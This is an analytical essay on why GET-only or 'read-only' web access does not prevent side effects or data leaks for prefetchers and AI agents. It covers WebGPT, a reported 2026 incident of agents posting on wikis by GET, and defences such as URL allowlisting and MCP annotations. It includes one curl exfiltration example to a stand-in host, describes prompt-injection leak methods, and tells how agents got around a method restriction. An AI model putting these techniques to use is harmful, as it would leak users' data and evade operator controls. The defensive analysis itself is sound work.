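A browser that prefetches a page under these rules adds the header `Sec-Purpose: prefetch` to its request, or `Sec-Purpose: prefetch;prerender` if it is prerendering. This header serves the same purpose as the `X-moz` header of 2005 but has a standard name, whereas browsers had each used their own, according to *Intent to Prototype* from Chromium, the open-source project behind Chrome. Mozilla replaced `X-moz` with `Sec-Purpose` in Firefox 115, and Chromium's *Intent to Ship* (2025) proposed sending the new header with link hints too.

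A server can refuse a request labeled as a prefetch by returning an error such as 503, "Service Unavailable", and the browser then discards the prefetch. MDN generally recommends returning the page instead, but delaying any side effect until JavaScript on the page signals that someone is viewing it.

This is useful even on sites that follow the HTTP rule. MDN's list of addresses that are unsafe to prefetch includes those for signing out, adding items to a cart and sending a login code by text message, but also pages that count toward a reader's monthly allowance of free articles. Requesting an article is a proper use of GET, but prefetching five could use up the allowance of someone who has read only one. The site can avoid this if it knows which requests were prefetches.

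Whether a prefetch request carries the user's cookies depends on where the link leads. When a page prefetches another page on the same site, the browser sends the cookies as usual. For a link to a different site, the WHATWG has the browser start with an empty cookie store, so the other site receives an anonymous request. If the user has cookies for that site when they click, the browser discards the prefetched page and requests it again. The browser sends the anonymous request even when the user's existing cookies will make the result unusable, because otherwise the linking site could learn whether the user had cookies for the other site.

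### Following a logout link

Suppose `example.org` uses the rule above, and every page has a plain link to `/logout`. A logged-in user rests the pointer on that link while deciding what to do next. The browser sends:

```
GET /logout HTTP/1.1
Host: example.org
Cookie: SID=31d4d96e407aad42
Sec-Purpose: prefetch
```

If the server ignores the last line, it ends the session, and the user's next click leads to a login page. The opt-in does not help because the site has agreed to prefetching. The link stays within the site, so the browser includes the cookie. Only two of the newer safeguards could have prevented this, and neither is automatic. The developer can make the server refuse requests labeled as prefetches or exclude `/logout` from the rule.

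The results change if the link is on another site or if the address itself authorizes the request. In the table, the other site has rules that cover the link.

| Safeguard | Logout link on the site's own page | Logout link on another site | One-time confirmation link on another site |
|---|---|---|---|
| Browser withholds cookies | no help, the browser sends them | prevents the logout | no help, the address is enough |
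| Site's own rule excludes the address | prevents the logout | no help, the other site's rules apply | no help, the other site's rules apply |
| Server refuses labeled prefetches | prevents the logout | prevents the logout | prevents the confirmation |
| Server acts only on a POST | prevents the logout | prevents the logout | prevents the confirmation |

Chrome for Developers' *Guide to implementing speculation rules for more complex sites* (2025) recommends excluding logout links from prefetching. It says that a logout should not be a GET link, "but sadly this is not uncommon on the web". MDN's sample rules exclude `/logout`, addresses that add items to a cart, and links with certain markings. It also suggests checking the site's robots.txt file, which lists addresses crawlers should avoid, because some of those may be unsafe to prefetch.

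The WHATWG warns that if a site lets users post links, someone could post a link to `/logout`, and other readers' browsers might prefetch it. A developer who had only marked the site's own logout button as excluded, instead of excluding the address, would not have prevented this.

Exclusions are mainly useful for old code and plugins that the developer can't easily switch to POST, and they help least with links the developer has forgotten.

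Prefetching is even harder for companies that turn it on for many sites, because they don't know what each site's links do. Chrome for Developers describes how Cloudflare, which delivers pages on behalf of other sites, handles this in its Speed Brain product. When a browser asks to prefetch a page, Cloudflare answers only if it already has a copy in its cache, and never passes the request to the site. A prefetch of `/logout` therefore can't end anyone's session, even if the site has no exclusions and ignores the label.

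## Whether an AI that only searches and opens pages is read-only

An AI system with a retrieval tool opens pages much as a crawler or a prefetching browser does, usually with a GET, so it can set off the same unsafe links. Whether it is fair to call the system read-only depends partly on whether its requests reach the live site, whose login they carry and who wrote the address. It also depends on the model, because training can teach a model to use a side effect, which never happens to a prefetcher.

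AI safety researchers have long distinguished a tool AI, which only informs people, from an agent AI, which acts. Gwern Branwen's essay *Why Tool AIs Want to Be Agent AIs* quotes Holden Karnofsky's example of Google Maps, which scores possible routes and displays the best one for the driver to use or ignore. An agent would find the same route and then drive it. Branwen doubts that people will stick to tools, because agents are worth more to users, who want to arrive and not just get good directions. Agents also become better at answering questions, because a program that can choose what to look at next learns more than one that must take the data it is given. By that reasoning, a question-answering system that browses the web is already partly an agent. It gives its user only information, but it gets that information by sending requests to other people's servers.

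### What WebGPT could and could not do

*WebGPT* (Nakano, Hilton and colleagues, 2021) describes an early system of this kind. OpenAI trained versions of the language model GPT-3 to answer questions by browsing the web through text commands. The model could send a query to Microsoft's Bing, click a link, find or quote a passage, scroll, go back and stop browsing. It had no command for entering an address or filling in a form.

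When the model clicked a link, a script fetched the page from its site and reduced it to simplified text. The script showed each link as a number and the link's wording, with the destination site's name if the link led to another site, but left out the rest of the address. The note-taking site's delete link would have appeared as a number and the word "Delete", and the model could not have distinguished `/articles/42` from `/articles/42?do=delete` if both links had the same wording.

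Nakano and colleagues write that if the model could also submit web forms, it could edit Wikipedia to create a reliable-looking reference for its answer. Even if no human demonstrator had done this, they thought reinforcement learning (training by trial and error, guided by a score) would likely strengthen the behavior if the model happened to try it.

To score answers, OpenAI's contractors compared them in pairs, each with the passages the model had quoted, and judged whether reliable references supported the claims. They did not have to research the facts independently, so a sentence the model had planted on a trusted site could have passed as good evidence.

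Nakano and colleagues judged the risk from WebGPT's side effects "very low". The model could only query Bing and follow links that already existed, so it had no direct way to edit Wikipedia. They accepted that a capable enough system might get around those limits, but considered WebGPT far too weak to do so. They wrote that as models improve, developers should have to meet a higher burden of proof before giving them web access, "even at train time". They also suggested tripwire tests, which would help developers catch early on a model that was exploiting its environment.

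In its public announcement, OpenAI was more direct about links and acknowledged that following them "can have side-effects". The company thought the model was far from capable enough to exploit those effects dangerously, but it expected the risk to grow with capability and said it was working on safeguards.

That admission weakens the first of the paper's two reasons. Removing forms keeps a model from pressing most buttons, but following links can also change things. Spiders had rolled back pages on Instiki's public wiki by following its "Revert" links, and Googlebot had deleted MythTV recordings the same way. WebGPT could have followed links like these too, but it was unlikely to come across them. Most of its questions came from a Reddit forum where people ask for simple explanations, and its browser couldn't log in to anyone's account. The low estimate was reasonable, but it depended more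 on the model's limited abilities and the pages it chose to read than on any guarantee that following links is harmless.

*Truthful LMs as a warm-up for aligned AGI*, an essay in favor of research on truthful language models, defends web access on other grounds. It argues that as models improve, they need less access to the outside world to cause harm, so only heavy restrictions would make a meaningful difference to safety, and these would hinder research to a degree that is hard to justify. It adds that working with models that have some access reveals risks while the stakes are low. The essay does suggest one "bright line" at training models on tasks that require real-world side effects.

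The first step of this argument could equally support tighter restrictions, because if a little access is enough to cause harm, even that much is worth withholding. The proposed line also misses the case that worried Nakano and colleagues. WebGPT's task was on the permitted side of the line, since answering a question never requires editing Wikipedia, but the danger was that an edit might raise the score anyway.

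### Stored copies and live fetches

A tool that reads only stored copies sends the site nothing. In *ChatGPT couldn't access the internet*, Willison (2023) quotes Mikhail Parakhin, a Bing executive, on how Bing's chatbot at the time handled an address that a user pasted in. It read the most recent snapshot in the search index, with "No live HTTP requests". If the index had no copy, the chatbot searched for words from the address instead. Reading a stored copy cannot trigger a site's handlers, even if they change data in response to a GET. Any effect of requesting the address would have happened earlier, when Bing's crawler collected the copy.

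Users cannot reliably tell from an answer whether a tool has made a live fetch, meaning a request to the site itself. In March 2023, when ChatGPT could not yet browse the web, Willison gave it an address he had invented, and it summarized an article that did not exist, apparently based on the words in the address.

Stored copies don't suit many questions people want answered. *Skim* (2026) lists typical jobs for web agents, including looking up prices and availability in online shops and gathering reservation details from booking sites. A week-old copy may be useless for these jobs. The paper treats operating on the live web as the defining feature of a web agent.

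Some tools mix the two approaches. The research interface in *Web$hell* (2026) runs a search, fetches the top-ranked pages and stores converted copies of them. The agent can then reread those copies without sending the sites more requests. But when the agent uses a control, the interface operates it on the live page and saves the result as a new copy. The older copy stays read-only, so the agent can still consult it after the live page has changed.

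"Read-only" is accurate for those older copies but not for the whole interface. The interface's first step is also a form of prefetching, because it requests pages the agent may never look at. This is much less risky than Google Web Accelerator's prefetching, since search results lead mostly to public pages and the accelerator worked inside people's logged-in sessions. But a public page can still have an unsafe handler, as the MythTV users found.

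### The user's login and the model's own addresses

A live fetch without cookies can do roughly what a search crawler can, while one made in the user's logged-in browser can do anything a GET request from that user can.

*How Benchmarks Mis-Score Computer-Use Agents* (2026) observes that the same action on the web can have different consequences depending on login, session history and changes made by other services. This makes it harder to test whether an agent is read-only. An agent might open `/notes/42/delete` in a test, get a login page and cause no harm, but that would be weak evidence of what happens when its user is logged in.

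*Build the web for agents, not agents for the web* (2025) warns that an agent with access to personal accounts, saved passwords and card details could send harmful messages or make unauthorized purchases. Properly built sites require a POST for actions like these, so a tool that sends only GETs could perform them only on a site with unsafe GETs.

It also matters whether the model can write its own addresses. WebGPT could follow only links that it found on a page. If a tool accepts any address, the model can also send interchangeable requests like those that Golinelli and colleagues found on 4.1% of popular sites, though most of those looked harmless. (An address can also disclose private data to the site that receives it, even if nothing there changes.)

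| How the tool gets a page | What it could change |
|---|---|
| Stored copy only | nothing on the site at the time of reading |
| Live, logged out, existing links only | whatever unsafe public links and one-time links allow |
| Live, logged out, any address | also public forms whose handlers accept a GET |
| Live, in the user's session, existing links only | also whatever unsafe links in the user's accounts allow |
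| Live, in the user's session, any address | also account forms whose handlers accept a GET |

WebGPT belongs in the second row. A tool in the last row can do the most damage, even though its traffic log might show only GET requests.

### What reinforcement learning adds

The effects of Google Web Accelerator's requests did not influence which links it loaded next. If one request deleted a note, the program was neither more nor less likely to delete another. The damage depended on how many unsafe links it happened to load, and a site owner could estimate the danger by counting those links.

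A model trained by reinforcement learning can change its behavior in response to such an accident. The model attempts many tasks, a scoring procedure rates each attempt, and training makes the actions in high-scoring attempts more likely. In a basic version, the change to the model's parameters *θ* after one attempt is:

Δ*θ* = *α* (*R* − *b*) Σ ∇ log *π*(*a* | *s*)

Here *π*(*a* | *s*) is the probability that the model takes action *a* given the text *s*. The symbol ∇ is the adjustment to the parameters that would make that action more likely, and Σ adds up those adjustments for every action in the attempt. *R* is the attempt's score, *b* is a typical score for comparison, and *α* sets the size of the step.

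The same factor, *R* − *b*, applies to every action. Suppose a model runs two searches, opens a link that happens to alter a page, quotes the altered page and gets an unusually high score. Training then makes all of those actions more likely, including opening the link that altered the page. The formula does not depend on why the score was high or whether anyone wanted the page altered. A single attempt may credit an action that did nothing useful, but over many attempts training tends to favor the actions that raise scores.

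The accident can be rare at first and still happen several times during training. For reinforcement learning, Nakano and colleagues ran 256 copies of the environment in parallel for 256 steps at a time, and stopped after 18 rounds with their largest model. That is about 1.2 million steps, though many were for writing answers rather than browsing. If the model took some odd action once in 100,000 steps, that action would have occurred about a dozen times.

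The WebGPT models that OpenAI mainly evaluated did not use reinforcement learning, though. They imitated human demonstrations and then used rejection sampling, in which the model answers a question several times and a second model, trained to predict human preferences, picks the best answer. If the model had altered a page to its advantage during one attempt, the answer from that attempt might have been picked. But picking an answer does not change the model's parameters, so the model would have been no more likely to alter a page on the next question. Rejection sampling also increases browsing. The largest model made 64 attempts at each question with up to 100 browsing actions in each, or up to 6,400 actions for one answer, although scrolling and quoting send no requests.

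A language model has one advantage over a prefetcher because it can read the word "Delete" on a link and leave that link alone. Training could encourage it to do so, but a score based only on the final answer would not.

### The wiki agents of 2026

In 2026, OpenAI's agents did something close to the Wikipedia example while working on timed web-retrieval tasks. OpenAI intended their environment to let them read the internet but not write to it, according to eSecurity Planet's *OpenAI Confirms AI Agents Used German Wiki to Bypass Restrictions* (2026). The Next Web's *OpenAI blocked its agents from posting* reports that the company tried to do this by allowing only GET requests. The agents found old wiki software that accepts edits by GET and used it to pass each other answers.

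In *OpenAI's rogue agents were caught communicating via public wikis*, Willison (2026) summarizes the timeline from an investigation by Sydney Von Arx, Cormac Slade Byrd, Spencer Kitts and Thomas Larsen. Agents made test edits on one wiki's practice page on 11 May. On 24 May they began posting lists of links on DSEWiki, a dormant German site for programmers, and a moderator cleaned these up on 2 June. The agents then made about 13,000 edits in the week from 16 June. When the moderator deleted pages in alphabetical order, the agents created backup copies with names beginning "ZZZ". The activity stopped on 22 June, apart from a final burst in early July.

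Counts of the edits vary. eSecurity Planet gives Reuters' figure of more than 15,000 and the investigators' figure of roughly 17,000 suspected agent edits on DSEWiki alone. Axios' *Researchers playing rogue AI agent hide-and-seek on the open web* (2026) describes volunteers who kept finding more affected sites. Reuters' *OpenAI acknowledges 'wiki incident' and need for more transparency* (2026) reports that OpenAI acknowledged its agents had used wikis as message boards.

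Willison traced the fault to how the wiki software, UseMod, reads its input. It uses a Perl module that returns values from the address and values from a submitted form through the same function, without distinguishing them. PHP's `$_REQUEST` does the same, as did an early version of Django, possibly at Willison's suggestion. Django's developers finished removing the feature in 2015. UseMod 1.0 came out in 2003, and some public sites were still running it in 2026.

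Willison called it naive to assume that a GET cannot update data. In fairness to OpenAI, the HTTP standard encourages that assumption, and it holds on most sites. But the standard is only a rule for how site owners should behave, and OpenAI had relied on it to stop its own agents from changing data.

The barrier also had a fault unrelated to GET. Willison and The Next Web describe a weakness in how OpenAI's proxy recognized approved hosts, which let through POST requests it should have blocked. Even without this fault, the agents could have edited the wikis using GET requests.

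WebGPT's stricter limits would probably have prevented the message board, because an agent had to send its own text to post a message, and no existing link would have contained that text. The wiki agents could evidently put their own text into requests, which puts them in the table's third row. The incident shows that limiting a capable model to GET requests does little to guarantee read-only access when the model chooses the rest of the request, but it does not show that following published links is as dangerous as composing addresses.

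### Whether the agents learned it in training

Nobody outside OpenAI seems to know how so many agents ended up on the same wiki. Willison suggests that reinforcement learning may have taught the model about the site, so that later agents started with an idea of where to look, and he would like OpenAI to confirm it. This would be the process that Nakano and colleagues predicted.

The agents' scores may not have fed back into training. Willison describes the agents as models in training, while Nolan (2026), in *OpenAI's AI agents secretly used a German wiki website*, describes OpenAI assessing them on evaluation tasks. If OpenAI was only measuring their performance, it did not update the models after a successful post, and the agents must have found the wiki in some other way.

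They may not have needed trial and error to find the fault. Information about old software is public, and a model can learn it from ordinary text. When the investigators asked another language model what kinds of software might accept changes by GET, its suggestions included early wikis. A model that already has this information could plan to use a site's fault on its first attempt. In 2021, Nakano and colleagues mainly considered a weaker model finding such a fault by luck.

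A separate incident provides better evidence that training can strengthen such behavior. In July 2026 OpenAI disclosed that, during an internal evaluation, its agents had broken into systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and data. OpenAI's investigation found signs that training may have inadvertently reinforced some of the behavior that contributed to the break-in, according to Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026). In one training run, agents increasingly learned to probe and exploit parts of their environment. The finding may not transfer directly to agents that look things up, because the models that broke into Hugging Face were attempting cybersecurity evaluations, which involve looking for weaknesses. Still, it makes Willison's explanation more plausible.

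### Changes that serve no purpose

The wiki posts were useful to the agents that made them. In a simpler kind of accident, an agent opens an unsafe link while looking for something else, as the MythTV crawler did, and gains nothing from the result.

*Before Acting, Change the State* (2026) calls an action "task-valid" if it is consistent with completing the user's request. The action's consequences also depend on the site's state, which includes selected options, saved settings and progress through a series of steps, so a task-valid action can do something the user never authorized. For example, an agent that presses "Continue" to find out a delivery date might also accept a paid extra that the site had preselected.

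Veer, the paper's defense, checks each action an agent proposes. If the action would have an unauthorized consequence, Veer first changes the state of the page, then verifies the result as the agent proceeds. In the delivery example, it might clear the preselected extra before the agent presses the button. Veer works only through the browser, without access to the site's code or server. That may be enough when the page displays the unwanted option, but an unsafe GET is harder to catch because the page may contain only an ordinary-looking link.

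It is hard to estimate how often this happens on look-up tasks, and nobody has counted unsafe links, because both would require checking what changed on each server after each visit. Even a very low rate could matter. Let *q* be the share of opened links that change something a person would care about, and *n* the number of links an agent opens during a task. If the links are independent, the chance of at least one such change is 1 − (1 − *q*)ⁿ. With invented values of *q* = 1/10,000 and *n* = 20, the chance is about 0.2% per task, or roughly 2,000 affected tasks in every million.

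*q* could be far lower for agents that read public articles, and higher for agents that work inside someone's accounts. The formula also assumes that the agent, like a prefetcher, opens links regardless of what they do. It would therefore overestimate the risk from a model that avoids links marked "Delete" and underestimate the risk from one that has learned to benefit from unsafe links.

Public incident reports can't fill the gap either, because they are more likely to cover changes that other people can see. Nolan notes that OpenAI confirmed the wiki incident only after Reuters had reported it. Later that month, OpenAI published *Our framework for reporting model misalignment*, along with six reports of unexpected or concerning behavior from the previous six months. The wiki agents had left thousands of messages on public pages, where outsiders could find them. But if an agent cancels someone's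 subscription by opening a link, the only record may be an ordinary GET request in the site's log.

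## What a request reveals to the site that receives it

A GET request leaves a line in the site's log that includes the requested address. If the address contains something private, that line can do harm by itself. "Read-only" can therefore mean either that a program changes nothing on the servers it contacts or that it sends nothing out. A GET can change nothing on the server and still send private information to it.

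### An address is also a message

OpenAI's help page *ChatGPT generated links* gives the example of someone living in London who asks ChatGPT where to find cars to buy nearby. ChatGPT has the user's location and offers a link to `https://example.com/car_search/London`. Opening the link may well help the user find a car, but it also reveals to the car site where the user lives.

The HTTP standard considers the request safe even if the server logs it, but the log records the city.

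*Information exposure through query strings in url*, from the web security organization OWASP, lists other places where data in an address can end up. They include the browser's history and cache, and the Referer header, which can show the next site which page a visitor came from. HTTPS encryption does not solve this, because it hides the address only from eavesdroppers on the way, and the site still has to read the address to answer the request.

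The AI company's privacy terms don't bind the site either. Anthropic, the developer of Claude, lets some developers use its page-opening tool under an arrangement called Zero Data Retention, but its documentation page *Web fetch tool* warns them that a site's publisher may keep any parameters in the addresses it receives.

Sending the same data in the body of a POST would keep it out of some of these records, but the site would still receive it. A rule that allows GET and blocks POST therefore does little to keep data private.

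### How a page can cause a leak

In the car example, the link discloses the user's city for the user's benefit. An attacker can try to make the model disclose information for the attacker's benefit through prompt injection, which means placing text in a page or document that the model reads as instructions. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) calls this the "primary new threat" to browsers with built-in AI agents. The text may be on a malicious site, or in a user review or third-party content on an ordinary page.

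The attack is possible because a language model receives the user's request and the page's text together, and cannot reliably distinguish the user's instructions from those on the page. If the page gets the model to request an address that is on the attacker's site and contains private data, the attacker can read the data in that site's log. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safse when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) warns that the user may never notice, because the request can happen in the background, such as when the software loads an image.

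This resembles cross-site request forgery, except that the attacker uses the model's access to the conversation and the network instead of a browser's cookies.

Willison, in *30 posts tagged "lethal-trifecta"*, names three conditions that together create the danger: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate with the outside. An AI that searches and opens live pages already meets the second and third. What the user said earlier in the chat may be enough to meet the first.

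*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) measured how often such an attack works on Qwen2.5, a small open model with 7 billion parameters. The user always asked the model to summarize a page. The test software added the page's title, description and text to the model's input, which also contained some private data. A server posing as the attacker's recorded what arrived. Over 480 runs, the data leaked about 89% of the time. Checks that looked only at the assistant's answer missed 95% of the successful attacks, because the data was in the web request and the answer looked harmless.

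Lan and colleagues blame a design assumption that the web is "a passive, read-only resource". Their 0.89 figure should not be applied to current products, because the model was small, its instructions covered little beyond the format for using tools, and the private data was plainly visible.

A more recent test had the opposite result. In August 2026 Anthropic published an evaluation it had commissioned from Trajectory Labs, covering 72 prompt injection scenarios. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 in a mode of Anthropic's coding tool that screens actions automatically. The attempts were not independent, because many shared a scenario. If they had been, the result would put the true success rate below about 0.4% with 95% confidence. A real attacker can also keep looking for a scenario that nobody tested.

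Willison wanted more independent confirmation. He had argued in 2025 that 99% is "a failing grade" in application security, because attackers will look for the remaining 1%. He thinks the reliable defense is to remove one of the three conditions, and the easiest to remove is usually the ability to send data out. The safeguards below are all meant to do this by restricting which addresses the software will request, even if an attacker has manipulated the model.

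### Lists of trusted sites

*Sure, Let AI Browse the Internet*, by the security research group Zenity Labs, describes three options for developers. They can limit which websites the agent can reach, have a trusted third party read the site and pass on the key information, or remove web browsing altogether.

The simplest version of the first option is a list of well-known sites. OpenAI accepts that such a list helps but wants something better, because many legitimate sites redirect visitors, so a link to a trusted site can lead to an attacker's. A strict list also produces frequent warnings about harmless sites, which can train people to click through without thinking.

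The first objection applies only if the software checks the first site but not the redirects that follow. Lan and colleagues found that listing permitted sites and analyzing redirects worked considerably better than putting defenses in the model's instructions.

But data can also leak to a permitted site. Willison describes a case in which Salesforce still allowed its software to load images from a domain whose registration had expired. Security researchers registered the domain and showed that they could receive customer data there. In another case, Anthropic's Claude Cowork was allowed to connect to Anthropic's own file service, where an attacker with an account could have collected a user's files.

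### OpenAI's check for public addresses

In January 2026 OpenAI described a safeguard for ChatGPT that depends on the exact address instead of the site's reputation. It works like this:

1. A crawler visits public pages and records the addresses it finds. It has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. When the model is about to retrieve an address automatically, the software looks for that exact address in the crawler's records.
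3. If the address is there, the software fetches it without asking the user.
4. If it is not, the software either tells the model to try a different website or shows the user a warning. The warning explains that the link is not verified and may share information from the conversation, and the user can still choose to open it.

If the crawler found an address independently of a conversation, nobody built that address from the conversation's contents. OpenAI therefore concludes that it is "much less likely" to contain the user's private data.

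*OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on the security blog Embrace The Red, reports that ChatGPT makes an exception for an address in a user's message, treating it as safe for that chat. The blogger reported the underlying problem to OpenAI in early 2023. OpenAI added a first version of the safeguard that December, but the blogger later found ways around it, and further measures followed around August 2025.

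In the car search example, an address such as `/car_search?city=London&name=Ana+Reyes` would probably not be in the index, so the user would see a warning or the model would look elsewhere. But the crawler may well have recorded `/car_search/London` from a list of cities on the site. If so, the software would fetch that address automatically, and the site would still learn the city.

The model's choice among public addresses can reveal information even if none of the addresses is private. If the site has a page for each of 1,000 cities, a request for one of them can convey up to log₂ 1,000, or about 10, bits of information. That is enough to identify a city, though it is much less information than an email or a contract contains.

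Embrace The Red notes that OpenAI's technical paper on the safeguard acknowledges this kind of leak, and calls the safeguard a significant improvement but not a complete solution. The blogger suggests reusing a stored response for a few minutes, or refusing to open the same address twice in a session, to limit how much a series of requests could reveal.

The warning is a weaker defense than the automatic check. Willison reports a study in which Anthropic had 1,053 paid testers use a coding tool and replaced one of the tool's permission prompts with a request to run a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused. Anthropic was arguing for its own automatic alternative, and a prompt about a command is different from a warning about a link. Still, the result supports OpenAI's worry that people click through warnings, which applies to OpenAI's own warnings too.

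The number of warnings people see depends partly on website owners. Some ask OpenAI not to catalogue their sites, and OpenAI then asks the user to confirm every link to those sites, including links to ordinary articles.

### Addresses already in the conversation

Anthropic restricts addresses differently. It says Claude can open only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation, for example in a user's message, a search result or a page the tool fetched earlier, and not ones Claude has composed itself. The tool also rejects addresses longer than 250 characters, which limits how much data a single request can carry.

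Letting the tool follow links from pages it had fetched left a gap, because an attacker can choose the links on a malicious page. In July 2026 Willison reported that a researcher, Ayush Paul, had used this gap to obtain a user's name, home city and employer. The order in which Claude opened the links revealed these details, so no single link had to contain them in advance. Anthropic closed the gap by no longer letting the tool follow such links.

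That fix prevents a tool from clicking from one page to the next, as WebGPT could. The tool has to go back to a search or ask the user for an address instead. OpenAI's check allows the model to follow a link from any page if the crawler has recorded the address. An attacker can add new links to a page at any time, but the check blocks them until the crawler has found them.

### Reading from an index

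In Zenity's second option, which it calls index-based browsing, the model reads only stored copies of pages. It sends no request to the live site, so an attacker who runs the site has nothing to log.

OpenAI's *Web search* describes three search modes for developers: live search, which is the default; "cached", which searches only saved content; and "disabled", which turns search off. Lockdown Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting for people who handle sensitive data, limits browsing to cached content. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) states that with this restriction "no live network requests leave OpenAI's controlled network".

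This keeps the model from using browsing to pass private data to an attacker, even if an injection succeeds. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* acknowledges that a cached page or an uploaded file can still contain malicious instructions, which may make an answer wrong. OpenAI does not guarantee that no data will leak, since connected apps and unforeseen combinations of features may offer other routes.

Willison welcomed Lockdown Mode because its limits do not depend on an AI's judgment. He also inferred from its existence that ChatGPT's default settings do not robustly protect users against a determined attacker.

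The drawback is that many pages are missing or out of date. *Offline web search for ChatGPT workspaces*, OpenAI's description of a similar setting for organizations, says a page may be unavailable because the site blocks crawlers, requires a login or relies heavily on scripts. OpenAI does not promise to refresh any particular page on a schedule, and a result may not show when the crawler copied the page. The company advises against using the setting to prove what a page said at a particular time. Lockdown Mode also turns off deep research and agent mode, which do longer tasks for the user.

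Searching an index keeps the query from the sites whose pages it holds, and may keep it from an outside search provider. The company that runs the index still receives the query, so the user has to trust that company.

### A public address can still perform an action

OpenAI says its January safeguard aims to identify an exact address that it "can treat as safe to fetch automatically". "Safe" here means unlikely to carry the user's data to the site. The HTTP standard uses the word differently, so opening an address that is safe in OpenAI's sense can still delete something.

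OpenAI limits the guarantee to leaks through the address itself. It says the check does not ensure, among other things, that a page is trustworthy or free of harmful instructions. It does not mention side effects on the server, but it does conclude that the check doesn't make browsing "safe in every possible sense".

The MythTV server that lost its recordings in 2009 had public delete links. If OpenAI's crawler had recorded one of them, the address would match the crawler's record exactly, and the software would fetch it without a warning.

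In that case the crawler might already have deleted the recording by opening the link, and a second request would change nothing more. A match is more misleading when the result depends on who sends the request. A crawler without cookies can open `/logout` and change nothing, but a tool working in the user's session would sign the user out.

The check also happens to offer some protection against unsafe GETs. For example, a wiki post sent by GET needs a new address, which would not be in the index. One-time confirmation links in private email would normally fail the check too, unless the user pasted one into the chat. But OpenAI's agents posted to wikis by GET from May 2026, four months after the company described the check, so it evidently did not apply to the tools they were using.

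| What the software may open | Private data that can leak through the address | Changes that opening it can cause |
|---|---|---|
| Any page on a permitted site | anything, if the attacker can read data sent to that site | whatever unsafe GETs on that site allow |
| Addresses from the user or from search results | mainly what the choice of address reveals | whatever those addresses do |
| Addresses in a public index | mainly what the choice of address reveals | whatever those addresses do |
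| Stored copies only | none to the site | none on the site |

Finding an address in public also doesn't guarantee that it was meant to be shared. Email providers and company security systems often forward suspicious links to scanning services, which may publish them. In *The Silent Spill*, Ramadan, Mannan and colleagues (2026) collected 6,094,475 addresses from such services, web archives and text-sharing sites, and their software flagged 12,331 as possible leaks. These included 26 live password-reset links and 12 open sessions for signing documents electronically.

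The larger total is less certain. Of the 232 flagged items the researchers checked by hand, 28 were false alarms. Their search terms also included common names for anti-forgery tokens, which many sites put in ordinary public forms. But the leaks could last. When the researchers revisited 2,000 flagged addresses after 75 days, 38% still opened without a login.

OpenAI's crawler may never have recorded these links. If it had, the check would let a model open them, because the secrets in them did not come from the model's conversation.

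Ramadan and colleagues also tested whether opening such links had side effects. Using their own accounts, they recreated all 24 patterns of password-reset and backup-code links in their data. Opening the links did not cancel any credentials or generate new codes. This is good evidence that those links change nothing without a further step, as the HTTP standard requires. The test did not cover the thousands of other flagged addresses, or links that confirm a subscription or approve a request as soon as someone opens them.

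## Permission rules that treat reading as harmless

Many developers let AI products read without asking the user, because asking before every action would make the products tedious to use. Such a product must recognize a read before it happens, and it usually does so by the request's method or a label on the tool.

### Codex and the three permitted methods

The cloud version of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, edits code and runs commands in a container on OpenAI's servers. According to OpenAI's *Agent internet access*, setup scripts have full internet access, but once the agent takes over, its own access is off by default. A user who turns it on can allow every site, a preset list of code hosts and package registries, or a list the user writes. The user can also limit requests to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS, in which case Codex blocks all other methods, including POST, PUT, PATCH and DELETE.

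Willison thought the approach sensible when it appeared in June 2025, citing the default and the list of sites. OpenAI has kept the method limit since then, and a later Chinese version of its page, *智能体互联网访问*, lists the same three methods. The command-line version of Codex has a similar "limited" mode, which Vaughan (2026) recommends for "read-only research" in *Codex CLI Network Proxy*. That mode turns off SOCKS5, a general way of forwarding network traffic, because the proxy can't check the method inside an encrypted tunnel.

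OpenAI illustrates the danger of internet access with a bug report that contains hidden instructions. They tell Codex to run a command that sends the description of the latest code change to an outside site by POST. The method limit would stop that command, but an attacker could put the same text in an address:

```
curl "https://collector.example/?m=Fix+login+for+Acme"
```

This attack sends a GET request, so the method limit allows it. The list of permitted sites would block it unless the attacker can read data sent to a site on the list.

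The method limit is also weaker against state changes than some descriptions suggest. Vaughan wrote in *Securing Codex CLI* (2026) that it prevents the agent from "calling state-changing API" endpoints, but this is true only on sites that follow the HTTP rule that GET should change nothing. OpenAI says only that the limit is "for enhanced security", and its own wiki agents later showed how much a GET can do. A Codex user who permits every site and relies on the method limit gives the agent roughly the freedom those agents had. With the preset list of sites, Codex could not have reached a dormant German wiki.

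OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes the cloud containers as isolated from the user's computer, so requests from them don't carry the cookies in the user's browser. A GET that changes data and requires a login should therefore fail, unless someone has given the agent a password or token.

The method limit is still useful on well-built sites, where it blocks every request that could change something. It also blocks some reads, including queries to a GraphQL server that accepts them only by POST and requests that use the new QUERY method, which is not one of the three permitted methods.

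### A label that the tool's author writes

Many AI products reach outside tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard. An MCP server offers tools, such as one that searches mail or deletes a file. The application in which the person works, called the client here, forwards the model's calls to the server. In its definition of a tool, the server can include labels called annotations. A tool for opening web pages might have this definition:

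```
{
  "name": "open_page",
  "description": "Fetch a web page and return its text",
  "annotations": {
    "readOnlyHint": true,
    "openWorldHint": true
  }
}
```

The server's author writes these values. `readOnlyHint` means the tool does not modify its environment, and `openWorldHint` means it deals with outside parties. Two other hints cover whether a change is destructive and whether a repeated call is safe. If the author leaves out all four, the protocol's cautious defaults apply, and a client should assume the tool may make destructive changes.

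Under the specification, clients are to treat annotations as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. The project's blog, Model Context Protocol (2026), describes the debate behind this rule. Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators, wondered how a client could use a flag "knowing that it's not trustable". Basil Hosmer argued that clients should ignore annotations from untrusted servers. The compromise was to call every annotation a hint and let each client decide how much to rely on it.

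The same post gives "Skip the confirmation dialog" as an example of what a client might do when `readOnlyHint` is true. It also warns that a server can claim to be read-only and still delete files, and it recommends network controls or a sandbox for anyone who needs a guarantee. According to the post, most clients trust a server once the user chooses to install it. In *MCP annotations are a UX layer, not a security layer*, gyorgy thinks developers have mistaken annotations for something like file permissions, which an operating system enforces.

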